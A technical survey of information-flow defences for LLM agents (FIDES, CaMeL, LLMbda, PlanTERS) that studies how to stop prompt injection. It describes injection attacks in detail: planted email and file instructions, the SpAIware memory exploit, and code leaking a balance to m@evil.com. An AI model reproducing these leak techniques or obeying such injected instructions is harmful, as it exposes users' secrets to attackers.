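Microsoft's sample policy for posting to a Teams channel uses robust declassification: it allows a post if the context is trusted or if everyone in the channel may read the content, and otherwise asks the user. That rule would be risky for Alex's inbox, because if the system treated emails from colleagues as trusted, the agent could send Marco the sales figures without asking. Robust declassification assumes that a release in a trusted context is intentional, but a model can also leak data by mistake.

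In GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding agent, users must turn the feature on with an experimental flag. It enforces policies for selected tools from the GitHub server and doesn't yet support other MCP servers. The package that defines GitHub's labels doesn't enforce them. According to pkg.go.dev's *ifc* (2026), a separate service enforces them, so an agent that ignores the labels gets no protection from them.

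Microsoft has also published a gateway that adds labels to other servers. For each tool, someone must describe the structure of its output, write a function that passes labels from arguments to results, and choose or write a policy.

### Prudentia: fewer requests for approval

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), who designed ELBA, defend strict policies in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* on the grounds that such policies save approvals. Their team includes most of the people who built FIDES.

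They also built Prudentia, a version of FIDES whose model is given the policies and the current labels. Before it opens a variable, the model must explain why it needs to and list the tool calls it plans to make afterwards. It can then ask the user to endorse the data instead of approving each later call. If a harmless email lists ten tasks, the user endorses the email once, rather than approving ten calls, and the agent carries out all ten tasks.

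Kolluri and colleagues used AgentDojo to measure the share of tasks an agent completed without any approval and the total number of approvals across the tasks it completed. Each cell in the table gives these two figures in that order. The basic agent asks for approval before every consequential call.

| Model | Basic agent | Basic agent with label checks | FIDES | Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|
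| GPT-4o | 28.0%, 59.4 | 38.4%, 39.4 | 50.3%, 7.8 | 42.5%, 23.8 |
| o3-mini | 24.3%, 48.2 | 35.5%, 32.4 | 50.1%, 18.8 | 59.1%, 16.4 |
| o4-mini | 32.8%, 48.6 | 42.5%, 34.6 | 53.2%, 36.8 | 59.4%, 19.2 |
| GPT-5 | 35.1%, 52.0 | 43.4%, 40.4 | 57.1%, 41.3 | 72.7%, 7.3 |

With GPT-5, Prudentia needed less than a fifth as many approvals as FIDES and completed slightly more tasks overall, 80.0% against 78.9%. With GPT-4o, it did worse than FIDES on both measures in the table, although it completed more tasks once the user could approve calls. The extra planning seems to require a strong reasoning model. Prudentia also cost about twice as much per task as FIDES with GPT-4o, the only model with price estimates.

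The approval counts come from runs without attacks, and the researchers assumed that the user would approve every request in a successful run, so the counts don't show whether people would notice a bad request. Noticing matters more with endorsement, because a user who endorses an email without spotting a hidden instruction removes the protection from every action that follows.

*Flowsh* (2026) describes a label-tracking command shell for agents and reports how it performed under attack. In 39 of 45 runs where the attacker's text reached the model, the shell's first approval request was for the attack itself, so no earlier requests would have worn the user down. In a setting designed for autonomy, however, the shell's completion rate on knowledge tasks was 35.3 percentage points lower than that of Lax, a comparison system.

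### FlowSeal's criticism of FIDES

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) studies people who trick an agent into revealing private data through ordinary requests. In the main example, Jane's agent has access to Mark's mental health diagnosis, and Mark's ex-wife Emily wants it. The researchers argue that defences fail if the model has to recognise a privacy risk in text that the attacker wrote. They apply this criticism to FIDES, saying that its language model performs all the policy enforcement.

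In FIDES, the model proposes a call, and separate code compares the labels and decides whether to run it. If Emily emails Jane's agent and asks it to fill in a shared page, her email is untrusted and the diagnosis has a label that excludes her. Once the agent has opened both, writing the diagnosis to the page fails both policies, however harmless the request sounds. Shim and colleagues didn't test this, because they left FIDES out of their experiments on the grounds that it has a different purpose and didn't fit into their benchmark.

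One weakness of FIDES in this setting is that it trusts the user's messages. If an operator let Emily talk to the agent as a user, robust declassification would allow the agent to send her the diagnosis.

In another of the attacks, the agent reveals private facts by deleting false ones. Emily shares a page that mixes true and invented facts about Mark and asks the agent to delete the entries that don't match its records. The agent writes nothing private, but the entries it leaves are the true ones. Suppose Jane passes this request on to the agent. FIDES could keep the records in variables and let the quarantined model choose which entries to delete. The AgentDojo policy for deletions would allow those calls, because it checks neither the labels of arguments nor confidentiality. A confidentiality policy for edits to shared pages would block the calls, but it might not stop information from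 leaking through whether the agent makes a call at all, which explicit secrecy doesn't cover.

Shim and colleagues' defence, FlowSeal, also uses code to intercept every outgoing call. If the agent has read private records and the recipient isn't on a trusted list, a separate language model decides whether the outgoing text reveals anything from those records. FlowSeal's security theorem doesn't cover this model's errors, so FlowSeal relies on a model's judgement where FIDES compares labels.

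The judgement worked well in the tests. The deletion attack leaked 2.3% of private items with FlowSeal, compared with 75.6% with one prompt-based defence. FlowSeal completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, close to the best competitor's 75.9%. With the checker set to block everything, utility fell to zero because the simulated data owners ignored requests for permission. With it set to allow everything, a related attack exposed 24.9% of private items instead of 0.5%. FlowSeal also withheld data it should have shared. When the owner would have consented if asked, it shared 32.7% of the requested items, compared with 61% to 86% for the other defences.

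## LLMbda: a label-tracking agent with a machine-checked security theorem

FIDES works only if labels follow data through the whole program around the model. Mistakes in that tracking are easy to make and hard to notice, because the agent behaves normally until someone exploits them. LLMbda is a small programming language for agents in which every value has a label. Garby and colleagues have proved in Lean that its label tracking is sound.

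Garby and colleagues compare LLMbda with CaMeL, which follows the dual-LLM pattern but has the planning model write a whole program before the agent reads any data. CaMeL's interpreter tracks labels and checks policies while the program runs. CaMeL has no comparable soundness theorem, and Garby and colleagues found ways to leak secrets that its tracking misses.

### A leak through the branch that doesn't run

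Suppose an agent manages a bank account, and an injected instruction tries to reveal whether the balance is high:

```
if account.balance > threshold:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

This is an implicit flow, a leak through the choice of branch, like the "Meeting cancelled" post that explicit secrecy doesn't cover. Because the condition reads secret data, CaMeL treats everything inside the branch as secret too and blocks the leak.

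An attacker can get around this with two variables, a trick that J. S. Fenton described in 1974:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Both variables start out public. When the program changes a variable inside a branch that depends on a secret, the tracker raises that variable's label to secret. The two possible runs go like this:

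| | Low balance | High balance |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp` after the first test | True, public | False, secret |
| `rich` after the second test | False, public | True, public |
| Email | Not sent | Sent |

With a high balance, `tmp` is false, so the program skips `rich = False`. The tracker doesn't process the skipped assignment and leaves `rich` public. With a low balance, the assignment runs, but `tmp` is still public, so `rich` stays public too. Either way, `rich` is a public copy of the secret, and the email passes the check.

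Austin and Flanagan, in *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*, describe a standard fix that stops the program if it tries to change a public variable inside a secret branch. With a high balance, the program above would stop at the first test. The fix also stops some harmless programs. If a program sets a variable to false in a secret branch and then always sets it back to true, the final value reveals nothing, but the fix stops the program before it can reset the variable. Austin and Flanagan therefore propose a third label for variables that may have leaked, which lets the program continue until it uses such a variable in a risky way, for example by branching on it.

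### Why retrying leaks more

Whether a program stops can itself reveal one bit of a secret. TACIT's guarantee excludes such leaks, and most label-tracking systems accept them too.

They become serious if something outside the tracked program reacts to the failure and tries again. CaMeL's interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop that does this. The loop has no labels, so nothing records that each attempt depends on how the previous one ended. A program could therefore leak a whole key, one bit per attempt. The CaMeL paper acknowledges the problem, and the system censors the error messages that pass between attempts, but it has no formal guarantee that this is enough.

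Garby and colleagues also found a simpler mistake in CaMeL's interpreter, which treats an untrusted value as trusted once a program inserts it into a text template.

### A language with conversations in it

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language built from functions. Each value has a label, a set that can contain `U` for untrusted and `S` for secret. An empty label means the value is trusted and public. A result computed from several values gets the union of their labels.

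Variables in LLMbda never change after the program defines them, which removes the two-variable leak. An `if` returns a value whichever branch runs, and that value gets the condition's label. The only thing that changes is the conversation with the model, which has its own label. A program can't prompt the model from inside a secret branch while the conversation is still public, because later replies could reveal which branch ran.

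Programs manage the conversation with three operations:

- `@p` adds the prompt `p` to the conversation, gets the model's reply and runs it as code. Plain data, such as a number or a text in quotation marks, counts as code that returns itself.
- `fork e` runs `e` on a copy of the conversation and then goes back to the original.
- `clear` empties the conversation.

With these, a developer can write a quarantined model as a short function:

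```
let quarantine = \prompt.
  let pair = fork (let _ = clear in @prompt) in
  pair.[1]
```

An agent can use a temporary conversation to extract an address from an untrusted email. The model sees only the prompt in that conversation, and its answer is untrusted because the conversation contained the email. The main conversation stays trusted. CaMeL and FIDES build this separation into their architectures, whereas in LLMbda a developer can use it wherever a task needs it.

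When the model replies with a function, the function runs under the same rules as the developer's code. It starts with the label of the conversation that produced it, so if that conversation contained an attacker's email, everything the function computes is untrusted.

Tools enforce policies with `assert`, which stops the program if a value's label violates the policy. In one example, Alice asks an agent to send a meeting reminder to whoever wrote the last email. The email is from Bob, but an attacker has added a postscript asking for a cancellation note instead. An ordinary tool-calling agent sent the cancellation. A second agent wrote its whole program before reading the email and used a mail function that accepts only a trusted subject and body. It sent the reminder. The policy doesn't cover the recipient's address, which comes from the email, so an attacker could still redirect the message.

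Checking a value's label can leak information. If a value is secret only when some hidden bit is 1, testing whether the value is secret reveals the bit. An earlier version of LLMbda had this problem when it used more than two levels of labels. Now the result of the test gets its own label, which depends on the test and not on the data. An `assert` returns no result, since the program either continues or stops.

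### The theorem

Noninterference normally requires that changing the secrets leaves the visible output unchanged. A language model samples its replies at random, so two runs can differ even with the same secrets. Garby and colleagues therefore compare the probabilities of the possible results.

Let $m$ be the highest label an observer can see, and let $e_0 \sim_m e_1$ mean that two programs, including their input data, differ only in parts that this observer can't see. Let $\mu_0(v)$ and $\mu_1(v)$ be the probabilities that each program finishes with the visible result $v$. The theorem, called termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, amounts to

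$$e_0 \sim_m e_1 \;\Longrightarrow\; \sum_v \max\big(\mu_0(v), \mu_1(v)\big) \le 1$$

If both programs always finish, each set of probabilities adds up to 1, and the condition can hold only if the two sets are identical. Suppose a program returns heads or tails with probability 0.5 each when a secret is 0, but heads with probability 0.6 and tails with 0.4 when the secret is 1. The sum would be $0.6 + 0.5 = 1.1$, so no LLMbda program can behave like this.

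Because the theorem is probabilistic, it does not compare individual runs. An observer may see different results with different secrets, but for programs that always finish, the difference is due only to chance.

The "termination-insensitive" qualifier weakens the guarantee more. If the program returned heads with probability 0.5 when the secret is 1 and otherwise never finished, the sum would be exactly 1, which the theorem allows. The theorem also allows a program that guesses a four-digit PIN at random, stops without finishing if the guess is wrong, and publishes the guess if it is right. Anyone who could restart this program freely would get the PIN after about 10,000 attempts on average, so the theorem protects a secret only if nothing outside LLMbda keeps retrying.

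*Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* (2008) describes leaks of this kind as the downside of a condition that is fairly permissive and easy to check. A program can leak more if it produces output as it runs. For example, it could count upward, post a message for each number, and hang when it reaches the secret. LLMbda's theorem compares only final results, and LLMbda's tools are functions that update a record of a simulated world. An agent with real tools would act before the run ended, so an observer could learn more. Garby and colleagues list this treatment of tools as a limitation. The theorem also doesn't cover side channels such as timing.

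The proof uses a modified way of running programs that skips any computation as soon as its label rises above $m$ and puts an empty value in its place. Write $\omega_0$ and $\omega_1$ for the probabilities of the visible results when the two programs run in this way. Skipping can't make a visible result less likely, since it only removes steps that might have failed. The modified runs also never use the hidden data, so they are the same for both programs:

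$$\mu_0 \le \omega_0 = \omega_1 \ge \mu_1$$

The probabilities in $\omega_0$ add up to at most 1, and neither program can exceed them for any result, which gives the condition above.

### Endorsement that can't release secrets

Some tasks require an agent to act on untrusted data. LLMbda has an explicit operation for this, `endorse [] x`, which returns the value of `x` with the `U` removed from its label. Because the operation is explicit, a reviewer can search a program for every place where the program relaxes the rules. In one example, the quarantined model sorts an email into one of a few categories, and the agent endorses the category and uses it as the subject of its reply.

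Every label has an integrity part $I$ and a confidentiality part $C$. If a program endorses a value with label $\ell$ to a target label $t$, and the surrounding code has label $pc$, the result has the parts

$$I = pc_I \sqcup t_I, \qquad C = pc_C \sqcup \ell_C$$

The target affects only integrity, so an endorsed secret is still secret. The result also can't be more trusted than the code that endorsed it. If an attacker's text led the model to write code containing `endorse`, that code would run as untrusted and its endorsements would do nothing.

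Garby and colleagues also prove an "insulated" version of the main theorem, which holds for any observer who ignores integrity, whatever the program endorses. It means that an attacker who chooses all the untrusted data still can't use an endorsement to reveal a secret. For integrity, the theorem holds only in programs without endorsements.

Developers can restrict endorsement further with two wrapper functions. One accepts only values from a fixed list, much like FIDES's typed answers. The other marks every endorsed value and refuses to endorse a marked value again. Without the second wrapper, one careless endorsement could make an attacker's text trusted, and code generated from that text could then endorse more. Neither wrapper has its own formal guarantee.

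### What Lean has checked

The Lean development contains the language's rules, the noninterference theorems and the interpreter that runs the agent. A further theorem shows that the interpreter produces each result with the probability the rules give it. According to Garby and colleagues, this is the first agent software with machine-checked security theorems about the program that calls the model. CaMeL's leaks came from details of its interpreter and from the loop around it, so proving theorems about the running program is worth the extra work.

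The theorems hold for any probabilities of the model's replies, even if the replies are chosen to help an attacker. But they assume that each reply is a fresh random sample that depends only on the conversation so far. A model service that carried over information from other conversations would break this assumption, and a secret from a forked conversation could then reappear in the main one. TACIT relies on a similar assumption about its trusted model.

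The interpreter contacts the model through a network function that Lean's proofs treat as a black box. The trusted base includes this function, Lean itself and the tool functions. Whoever writes the tools has to label data correctly and check labels before every sensitive action.

### Randori, an agent that practises first

Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori in LLMbda. Like CaMeL, it writes a program for the user's task, but it has to handle failed attempts differently. If it ran a faulty program on real data and showed the model the error, the conversation could become untrusted, and so would the next program. Retrying could also repeat a payment that had already gone through.

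Randori therefore practises on invented data. In practice mode, payments do nothing and every file contains the same placeholder text. The model fixes its program until the program runs without errors or the model runs out of attempts. It then writes a final version, which runs on the real account. The model writes all this code, including any endorsements, before the agent reads real data. Practice doesn't reveal label violations, though, because the invented data is trusted. The agent finds out about them only when the real run fails.

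The agent has eleven banking tools, and text from files is labeled untrusted. The program can send money only to a trusted recipient who is allowed to read the amount, subject and date. But the policy for scheduling a payment requires only a trusted amount, so a program could schedule a payment to an account number from an untrusted file without endorsing anything. The paper also lists no untrusted label for incoming transactions, although outsiders write their subject lines. The theorem guarantees that LLMbda enforces the policy, so it doesn't rule out these weaknesses in the policy itself.

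### Results on AgentDojo's banking tasks

Garby and colleagues tested Randori on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks and nine attacks with three models and ran everything three times. They also reran CaMeL with two of the models, with and without its policies. The table shows the share of tasks completed when there was no attack. A dash marks a combination they didn't report.

| Model | Randori | Randori, no endorsement | CaMeL, no policies | CaMeL, policies |
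|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 75.0% | – | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0% | 62.5% | – | – |
| MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6% | 54.2% | 70.8% | 37.5% |

With only 16 tasks, the 95% confidence intervals extend about 19 to 27 percentage points on either side. The effect of endorsement is within that range, but it has a clear cause. Three of the tasks ask the agent to read a file and act on it, which is impossible if the agent can't endorse anything in the file.

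Under attack, Randori completed 59.5% to 65.0% of tasks. Garby and colleagues conclude that it provides near-perfect security with the same utility as CaMeL without policies. The comparison favours Randori, because Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and lets the planning model endorse data by itself. CaMeL's score with policies shows how much stricter rules reduce utility when nobody can make an exception, much as ELBA's score did on the Slack tasks.

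Two of the 1,296 attacked runs ended in a successful attack, but most of the attacks had little chance of succeeding. The 16 tasks and nine attacks make 144 pairs, and in 97 of them the attack needs an action that the program for the user's task would never contain. For example, a program that summarizes recent transactions has no call that sends money. Because the model writes the program before reading any data, an injected instruction can't add that call, even without labels.

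In the other 47 pairs, the user's task involves actions that an attacker could misuse, so labels might matter. Randori resisted 421 of the 423 attacks in these pairs. But CaMeL without its policies also resisted all 141 attacks with GPT-5.2 and 138 of 141 with MiMo-v2.5. Since most of these attacks fail even when nothing enforces the labels, the benchmark is a weak test of enforcement. The theorem is better evidence that LLMbda's labels work.

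Garby and colleagues apply the same split to TACIT and ELBA. They argue that every attack on those systems tests the type checks, because both systems let a model write new code after seeing untrusted data. This isn't quite right for TACIT's AgentDojo tests, which also hid the untrusted text from the planning model.

Planning before reading can fail too. One task requires the agent to read a file and follow the file's instructions exactly. In two runs without policies, CaMeL's model wrote a program that translated each instruction in the file into a tool call. The program was fixed in advance, but the file's contents determined which actions it took, and the attacks succeeded.

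### When the file is false

Both of Randori's failures involved the same task and the same attack. The user asks the agent to read a text file, such as a bill, and make the payment it describes. The attacker has replaced the contents with a false payment request. Randori's program, written before the agent opens the file, extracts the payment details and endorses them, so the attacker gets the money.

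Randori faced this combination in only nine of the 1,296 runs, three with each model. Both failures were with GPT-5.2, so the attack worked in two of that model's three runs. For someone who regularly pays bills from files, that rate is more relevant than the overall rate of two in 1,296.

The user wants the recipient to depend on the file, but integrity noninterference forbids this. An agent that pays whichever company the bill in the file names will also pay an attacker who can write a convincing bill, even if the model never mistakes data for instructions. Without endorsement, LLMbda blocks both the attack and the honest payment. FIDES would do the same with the December bill if it checked arguments.

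The restricted forms of endorsement don't help here. Account numbers don't fit on a short fixed list, and the program endorses each value only once, so the wrapper against repeated endorsement has nothing to block.

Garby and colleagues argue that a user who asks the agent to pay the bill in a file has already decided that the agent should trust the file, and that the endorsement only records this decision. A similar attack succeeded against CaMeL, whose designers put it outside their threat model. The argument is a fair account of why labels can't settle the case, but the user probably meant to trust the company that sent the bill, not whoever edited the file last. A system could get closer to what the user meant by labelling files according to who can change them, or by asking the user to confirm any account that has never received a payment before. The first would need reliable records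 of who wrote what, and the second would take some of the user's attention.

The case also shows how much Randori depends on its planning model. Garby and colleagues acknowledge that nothing stops an overly permissive model from endorsing anything. An attacker can't prompt the model to do this, because it writes the program before the agent reads any real data, but the model can still misidentify which data the user meant to trust. In Randori's normal configuration, the theorem therefore protects secrets, but the safety of a payment based on a file depends partly on whether the model identifies trusted data correctly.

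## PlanTERS: proving that prompt injection adds no new leak

LLMbda's theorem guarantees that nothing an outsider sees reveals a secret. Many useful agents can't meet that standard because their job is to tell outsiders something about the user. Suppose Alice's assistant answers emailed meeting requests with the times she is free. Its replies depend on her private calendar, so it violates noninterference even when nobody attacks it. Simply accepting a request also violates noninterference because, as *Trident* (2026) points out, the sender learns that the user is free at that time.

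*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) proposes a weaker standard called relative security. It compares the agent with a reference agent, which runs the same plan under the same monitor but never obeys untrusted text. The real agent passes if all its leaks also occur in the reference agent. PlanTERS (Plan-Then-Execute Relative Security) is Dongol's framework for proving which agents pass.

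### The plan in place of a release policy

Systems traditionally permit some disclosure through declassification, where a policy lists what the agent may release. For Alice's assistant, the policy might let it share her free times with anyone who requests a meeting. Someone has to write such a policy for every task. Relative security uses the plan instead of this policy, and treats anything the plan discloses without an attack as acceptable.

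This saves work only if the plan is right. If a careless planner writes a plan that sends Alice's whole calendar, including her medical appointments, the reference agent discloses those appointments, so a real agent that does the same still counts as relatively secure. Dongol assumes a trusted planner, but also proves that if the reference agent discloses at most certain facts, a relatively secure agent discloses at most the same facts under attack. A reviewer can therefore examine the plan without thinking about injections.

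Whether Alice's assistant sends its reply depends on an outsider's email. Robust declassification, which FIDES uses for emails, would therefore reject the assistant unless someone endorsed its check for a meeting request.

### What counts as a new leak

Dongol studies plan-then-execute agents, which, like CaMeL, fix their plan before reading anything untrusted. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) notes that text planted in a user's calendar can't add a call, but can still change the body of a planned email.

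In Dongol's version, the model also helps carry out the plan, for example by summarising an email, and it may then try to make calls of its own. A runtime monitor allows or denies every call and every read of untrusted content. The attacker writes the untrusted content and chooses which texts the model treats as instructions, what call each one produces, and when the model obeys.

A leak consists of two runs, $r_1$ and $r_2$, with different secrets. The attacker supplies the same content in both but sees different results:

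$$\mathrm{Act}(r_1) = \mathrm{Act}(r_2), \qquad \mathrm{Obs}(r_1) \neq \mathrm{Obs}(r_2)$$

Here $\mathrm{Act}$ is the attacker's content and $\mathrm{Obs}$ is what the attacker observes. The agent is relatively secure if, for every such leak, the reference agent also has two runs that leak, with the same secrets and starting memory.

The reference agent's runs may use different attacker content. Suppose an email contains no meeting request but tells the assistant to send the calendar, and the model obeys. The reference agent would ignore this email, but it would send the same calendar in reply to a genuine request. Relative security therefore accepts the disclosure, although Alice didn't authorise it. If the email also asks for a password-reset code that the assistant holds, and the model sends both, relative security rejects the disclosure, because no email could make the reference agent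 send the code.

The idea comes from research on processors. To save time, a processor guesses which branch a program will take and starts running it. In a Spectre attack, a wrong guess leaves traces of secret data that an attacker can detect. In *Relative Security*, Dongol, Griffin and colleagues (2024) compared a processor that guesses with one that never does, and asked whether guessing allowed any new leaks.

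Because the reference agent may use different content, the definition can accept an injection that reveals more than an honest exchange would. For example, a plan might let an outsider make one guess at a PIN and answer only "right" or "wrong", while an injection makes the agent send the PIN itself. The definition accepts this disclosure because, for any two PINs, the reference agent could reveal the difference if the attacker guessed one of them. Dongol also defines a stricter, uniform version that rejects the disclosure. In this version, the reference agent's content may depend on what the attacker actually sent but not on the secrets.

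### A summariser with and without a fence

In Dongol's simplest example, Alice asks her agent to summarise an email. The plan has three steps:

```
ReadT  secret            Alice's account number
ReadU  mail Inbox        the untrusted email
Assign summary (...)     a summary of mail
```

The plan makes no outgoing call, but the agent has a `Fetch` tool for opening web pages. In the email, the attacker tells the agent to fetch an address on the attacker's site with the account number attached. After the agent reads the email, the model follows this instruction, and the agent sends the request before the plan reaches its third step. Two runs with different account numbers produce different requests, while the reference agent never requests anything. These runs prove that the agent leaks and give developers a concrete test case.

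A fence prevents the leak. The monitor withdraws `Fetch` as soon as the agent reads the email, so it denies the injected call and the attacker sees nothing. The fence doesn't interfere with the plan, which never fetches a page. If Alice had asked the agent to answer the email, a fence on the sending tool would have blocked that reply too.

The monitor can also let the plan decide when to withdraw a tool. In another group of examples, the plan calls `Lock`, and the monitor then denies all sending for the rest of the run. The position of that call matters:

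| Fence | Order of steps | What an injected call can send |
|---|---|---|
| Late | Read email, read secret, lock | The secret |
| Middle | Read email, lock, read secret | Data already in memory, such as notes from an earlier session |
| Early | Lock, then read email | Nothing |

Experience with processors is a poor guide to stopping prompt injection. A programmer can stop a Spectre attack by placing a fence just before the instruction that leaks, because that instruction is already in the program. A prompt injection adds a new leaking call, which the model may make at any time after reading the email.

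### Approving a tool or an exact call

An approval lets an agent use a tool after reading untrusted text. Dongol models an agent that repeatedly reads an email, receives a reply that Alice has approved, and sends that reply. The agent's memory holds private data. The plan has no step that sends this data, but the attacker's email contains an instruction for the model to send it.

With tool approval, Alice's approval permits the next sending call, whatever it contains. The model follows the instructions in the email after Alice has approved her reply but before the plan sends it, so the private data goes to the attacker. The injected call uses up the approval, so the monitor then blocks Alice's own reply. The `ApprovedApply` rule in ETAS has a similar weakness, because it doesn't tie an approval to a particular patch.

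With call approval, Alice permits only a call that sends exactly the reply she approved. The monitor denies the injected call unless the private data is identical to that reply. Either way, the attacker receives one message with the approved text. But if the two texts are identical, the injected call sends the message one step earlier than the plan would have, so an attacker who can time the message could learn whether the private data equals Alice's reply. This hardly matters for a long document, but it might for a short code if the attacker could influence many of her replies.

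Dongol treats Alice's approval as a trusted input, but it may not deserve that trust. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* reports that users of that coding agent approve 97% of its permission prompts. Most of those commands are probably safe, but someone who approves out of habit could approve the exact text of a harmful message. Sending it would still satisfy relative security, because the reference agent would send the approved message too.

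### The fence theorem

Dongol's main theorem covers every possible plan. Let $R$ be the set of tools that the monitor withdraws when the agent first reads untrusted content. The agent is relatively secure if all of these conditions hold:

- Injected text can request only calls to tools in $R$, and no trusted input gives those tools back.
- Each injection is a single call, which delays the plan's next step but doesn't replace it.
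- The model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance. Its timing can't depend on a secret or on the monitor's answers, although the contents of a call may depend on anything in the agent's memory.
- The attacker sees the contents and order of the calls that reach them, but not their timing or the calls that the monitor denies.
- The run ends.

The proof compares the two agents step by step. When the real agent makes an injected call, the reference agent waits. The monitor denies the call without changing its own state, so both agents can continue as before. Every other step belongs to the plan, and both agents take it. The attacker therefore receives the same messages from both. This is more than relative security requires, and it also satisfies the uniform version.

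A second theorem covers agents that run in an endless loop, provided that the model can't keep obeying injections forever. The monitor may restore the tools when a new session starts with an empty context. If it restores them while an old email is still in the context, the model can obey that email and leak the next secret.

The condition on $R$ is the most demanding in practice, because an operator can't control which tools an attacker will request in an email. To cover every single-call injection, the fence would have to withdraw every tool, and the agent could then only compute and show Alice the result. Narrow tools make the fence less restrictive. In one of Dongol's examples, a mail server has a separate sending tool for each recipient, and the fence leaves only the tool for the person Alice wants to write to. The model then can't send mail to the attacker, but the theorem doesn't cover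 injected messages to that person.

The fixed schedule excludes models that react to a refusal by trying something else, as FIDES's agent could. The result probably extends to such models, since the fence would deny the new attempt too, but Dongol leaves this to future work.

The trusted base includes the planner, the interpreter that runs the plan, and the monitor, which must check every call and every untrusted read. Showing Alice an answer must also have no effect that the attacker can see. For example, if her screen loads an image from an address in the answer, that request can leak a secret without the monitor checking it.

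### What 25 small agents show

The theory and examples are about 31,600 lines of Isabelle/HOL, a proof assistant. Dongol produced the theorems and proofs with the help of Claude Code, and Isabelle checked every proof. The proofs establish whether 25 small agents are secure. Ten are secure, nine leak, and the security of the other six depends on what the attacker can see or how the model may misbehave. Most of the proofs that an agent is secure cover only the particular attack in that example.

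Some of the leaks come from defences that look reasonable. For example, one monitor allows a single email per run. The injected call uses that email to send the reset code, and the monitor then blocks the planned reply. The limit works if the plan sends its own email before the agent reads anything untrusted.

Spotlighting marks untrusted text and adds an instruction not to obey it. It fails against a worst-case model whenever the marking keeps different texts distinct, because that model can respond to the marked text just as another model would respond to the original. The proof doesn't show how often real models would do this.

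A dual-LLM agent can leak through an implicit flow even if it labels data as CaMeL normally does. In Dongol's example, the quarantined model reads an outsider's email and Alice's private notes, and the plan sends the outsider a 1 or a 0 depending on the model's answer. Injected text can make that answer depend on the notes. Dongol doesn't model CaMeL's stricter mode, which is designed to prevent such leaks.

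Injected text might also make the model run a whole program. The program could leak a secret without making any calls itself, by copying the secret into a variable that the plan sends later. The fence can't stop this, because the plan makes the outgoing call. Dongol proves that a sandbox prevents this leak if it discards the program's changes and the fence blocks the program's reads as well as its calls.

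Another example is based on SpAIware, a published attack on ChatGPT. A web page made ChatGPT store an instruction in its long-term memory. In later conversations, the instruction made ChatGPT show images whose addresses contained the user's messages, which sent those messages to the attacker. A fence that restores tools in each new session fails here, because the memory brings the attacker's text back. The fence works if the monitor treats stored memories as untrusted content.

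### Limits of relative security

Relative security requires a plan that exists before the agent reads untrusted data, because otherwise there is no reference agent. The plan may contain branches and loops, so Alice's assistant can check whether an email requests a meeting. But it can't handle a request to do whatever a supplier's email asks if nobody foresaw the actions involved.

AgentDojo rarely tests such requests. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) counts only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks as needing a plan that changes along the way. CaMeL, which also fixes its plan first, completed none of AgentDyn's 60 open-ended tasks with any of the four models in the main comparison. On a benchmark introduced with *Trident*, where the data usually determines part of the plan, CaMeL with GPT-4.1 completed the task in 116 of 1,215 runs. CaMeL's data-flow policy also contributed to the failures,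 since in 574 runs it blocked a harmless call because the call depended on untrusted data.

Dongol also excludes tools whose replies depend on the request, which rules out many research agents. An attacker who runs a search engine, for instance, can choose its results after seeing a query that contains private data.

The definition also doesn't cover hijacking that leaks nothing. An injection that deletes Alice's files or makes a fixed payment may reveal nothing about her secrets, so an agent that obeys it can still be relatively secure. A fence that covered the tools involved would block those calls, but relative security doesn't require a fence to cover them.

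A monitor that blocks everything also counts as secure, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and is blocked too. One of the 25 agents passes largely because its monitor refuses every message computed from Alice's private notes, including the honest reply. Dongol says developers must check task completion separately, and reports no utility scores or tests with live models.

Removing a tool can turn a secure agent into an insecure one. Suppose a plan emails a report to an outsider, and an injection makes the agent send the same report to that outsider through a web request. The agent is relatively secure, because the outsider would have received the report anyway. If an operator removes the email tool but leaves web access, the reference agent no longer discloses the report, so the same web request becomes a new leak. Developers therefore have to repeat the analysis whenever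 they change an agent's tools, even if they only remove one.

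## Kernel packet filters: the first code shipped with its proof

LLMbda and PlanTERS rely on theorems that researchers proved in advance about a language or a kind of agent. In proof-carrying code, each program comes with its own proof. *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking* (Necula and Lee, 1996) tried this on packet filters, small programs that examine each packet arriving from a network and decide whether an application should receive it.

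A packet reaches the kernel, the core of the operating system, before it reaches any application. Passing every packet to an application that needs only a few wastes time, so operating systems let applications install a filter inside the kernel. But faulty or hostile code there could read or overwrite the kernel's memory. The usual defence in 1996 was the Berkeley Packet Filter (BPF). Applications supplied filters in a small, restricted language, and the kernel interpreted them and checked every memory access as it happened, which was safe but slow.

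### From machine code to a proof

Necula and Lee's method has four steps:

1. The kernel's designers publish a safety policy. It contains the axioms that proofs may use, a precondition that states what the kernel guarantees when it calls a filter, and a verification-condition generator, which turns machine code into a logical statement.
2. The filter's producer runs the generator on the filter. The resulting statement is the proof obligation. If it is true, no run of the filter can break the policy.
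3. The producer finds a proof and sends it along with the code.
4. The kernel runs the generator on the code it received and checks that the proof establishes the resulting statement. If it does, the kernel runs the filter without any further checks.

The kernel computes the obligation itself, so an attacker gains nothing by changing the code after the proof is finished. The changed code would normally have a different obligation, which the old proof wouldn't prove. If the old proof is still valid, the changed code is safe too. A digital signature, by contrast, shows only who supplied a program, and a trusted supplier can sign an unsafe one.

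Necula and Lee wrote their proofs in LF, a typed language in which a proof is a value and the statement it proves is the value's type, so checking a proof is ordinary type checking. Their checker was about five pages of C.

### A bounds-checked read

When the kernel calls a filter, register $r_1$ holds the packet's address and $r_2$ its length in bytes. The length is at least 64, the minimum for an Ethernet packet. The precondition says this about reading:

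$$\forall i.\; (0 \le i < r_2 \,\land\, i \bmod 8 = 0) \Rightarrow \mathrm{rd}(r_1 \oplus i)$$

Here $\mathrm{rd}(a)$ means that the filter may read the eight-byte word at address $a$, and $\oplus$ and $\ominus$ are the processor's 64-bit addition and subtraction.

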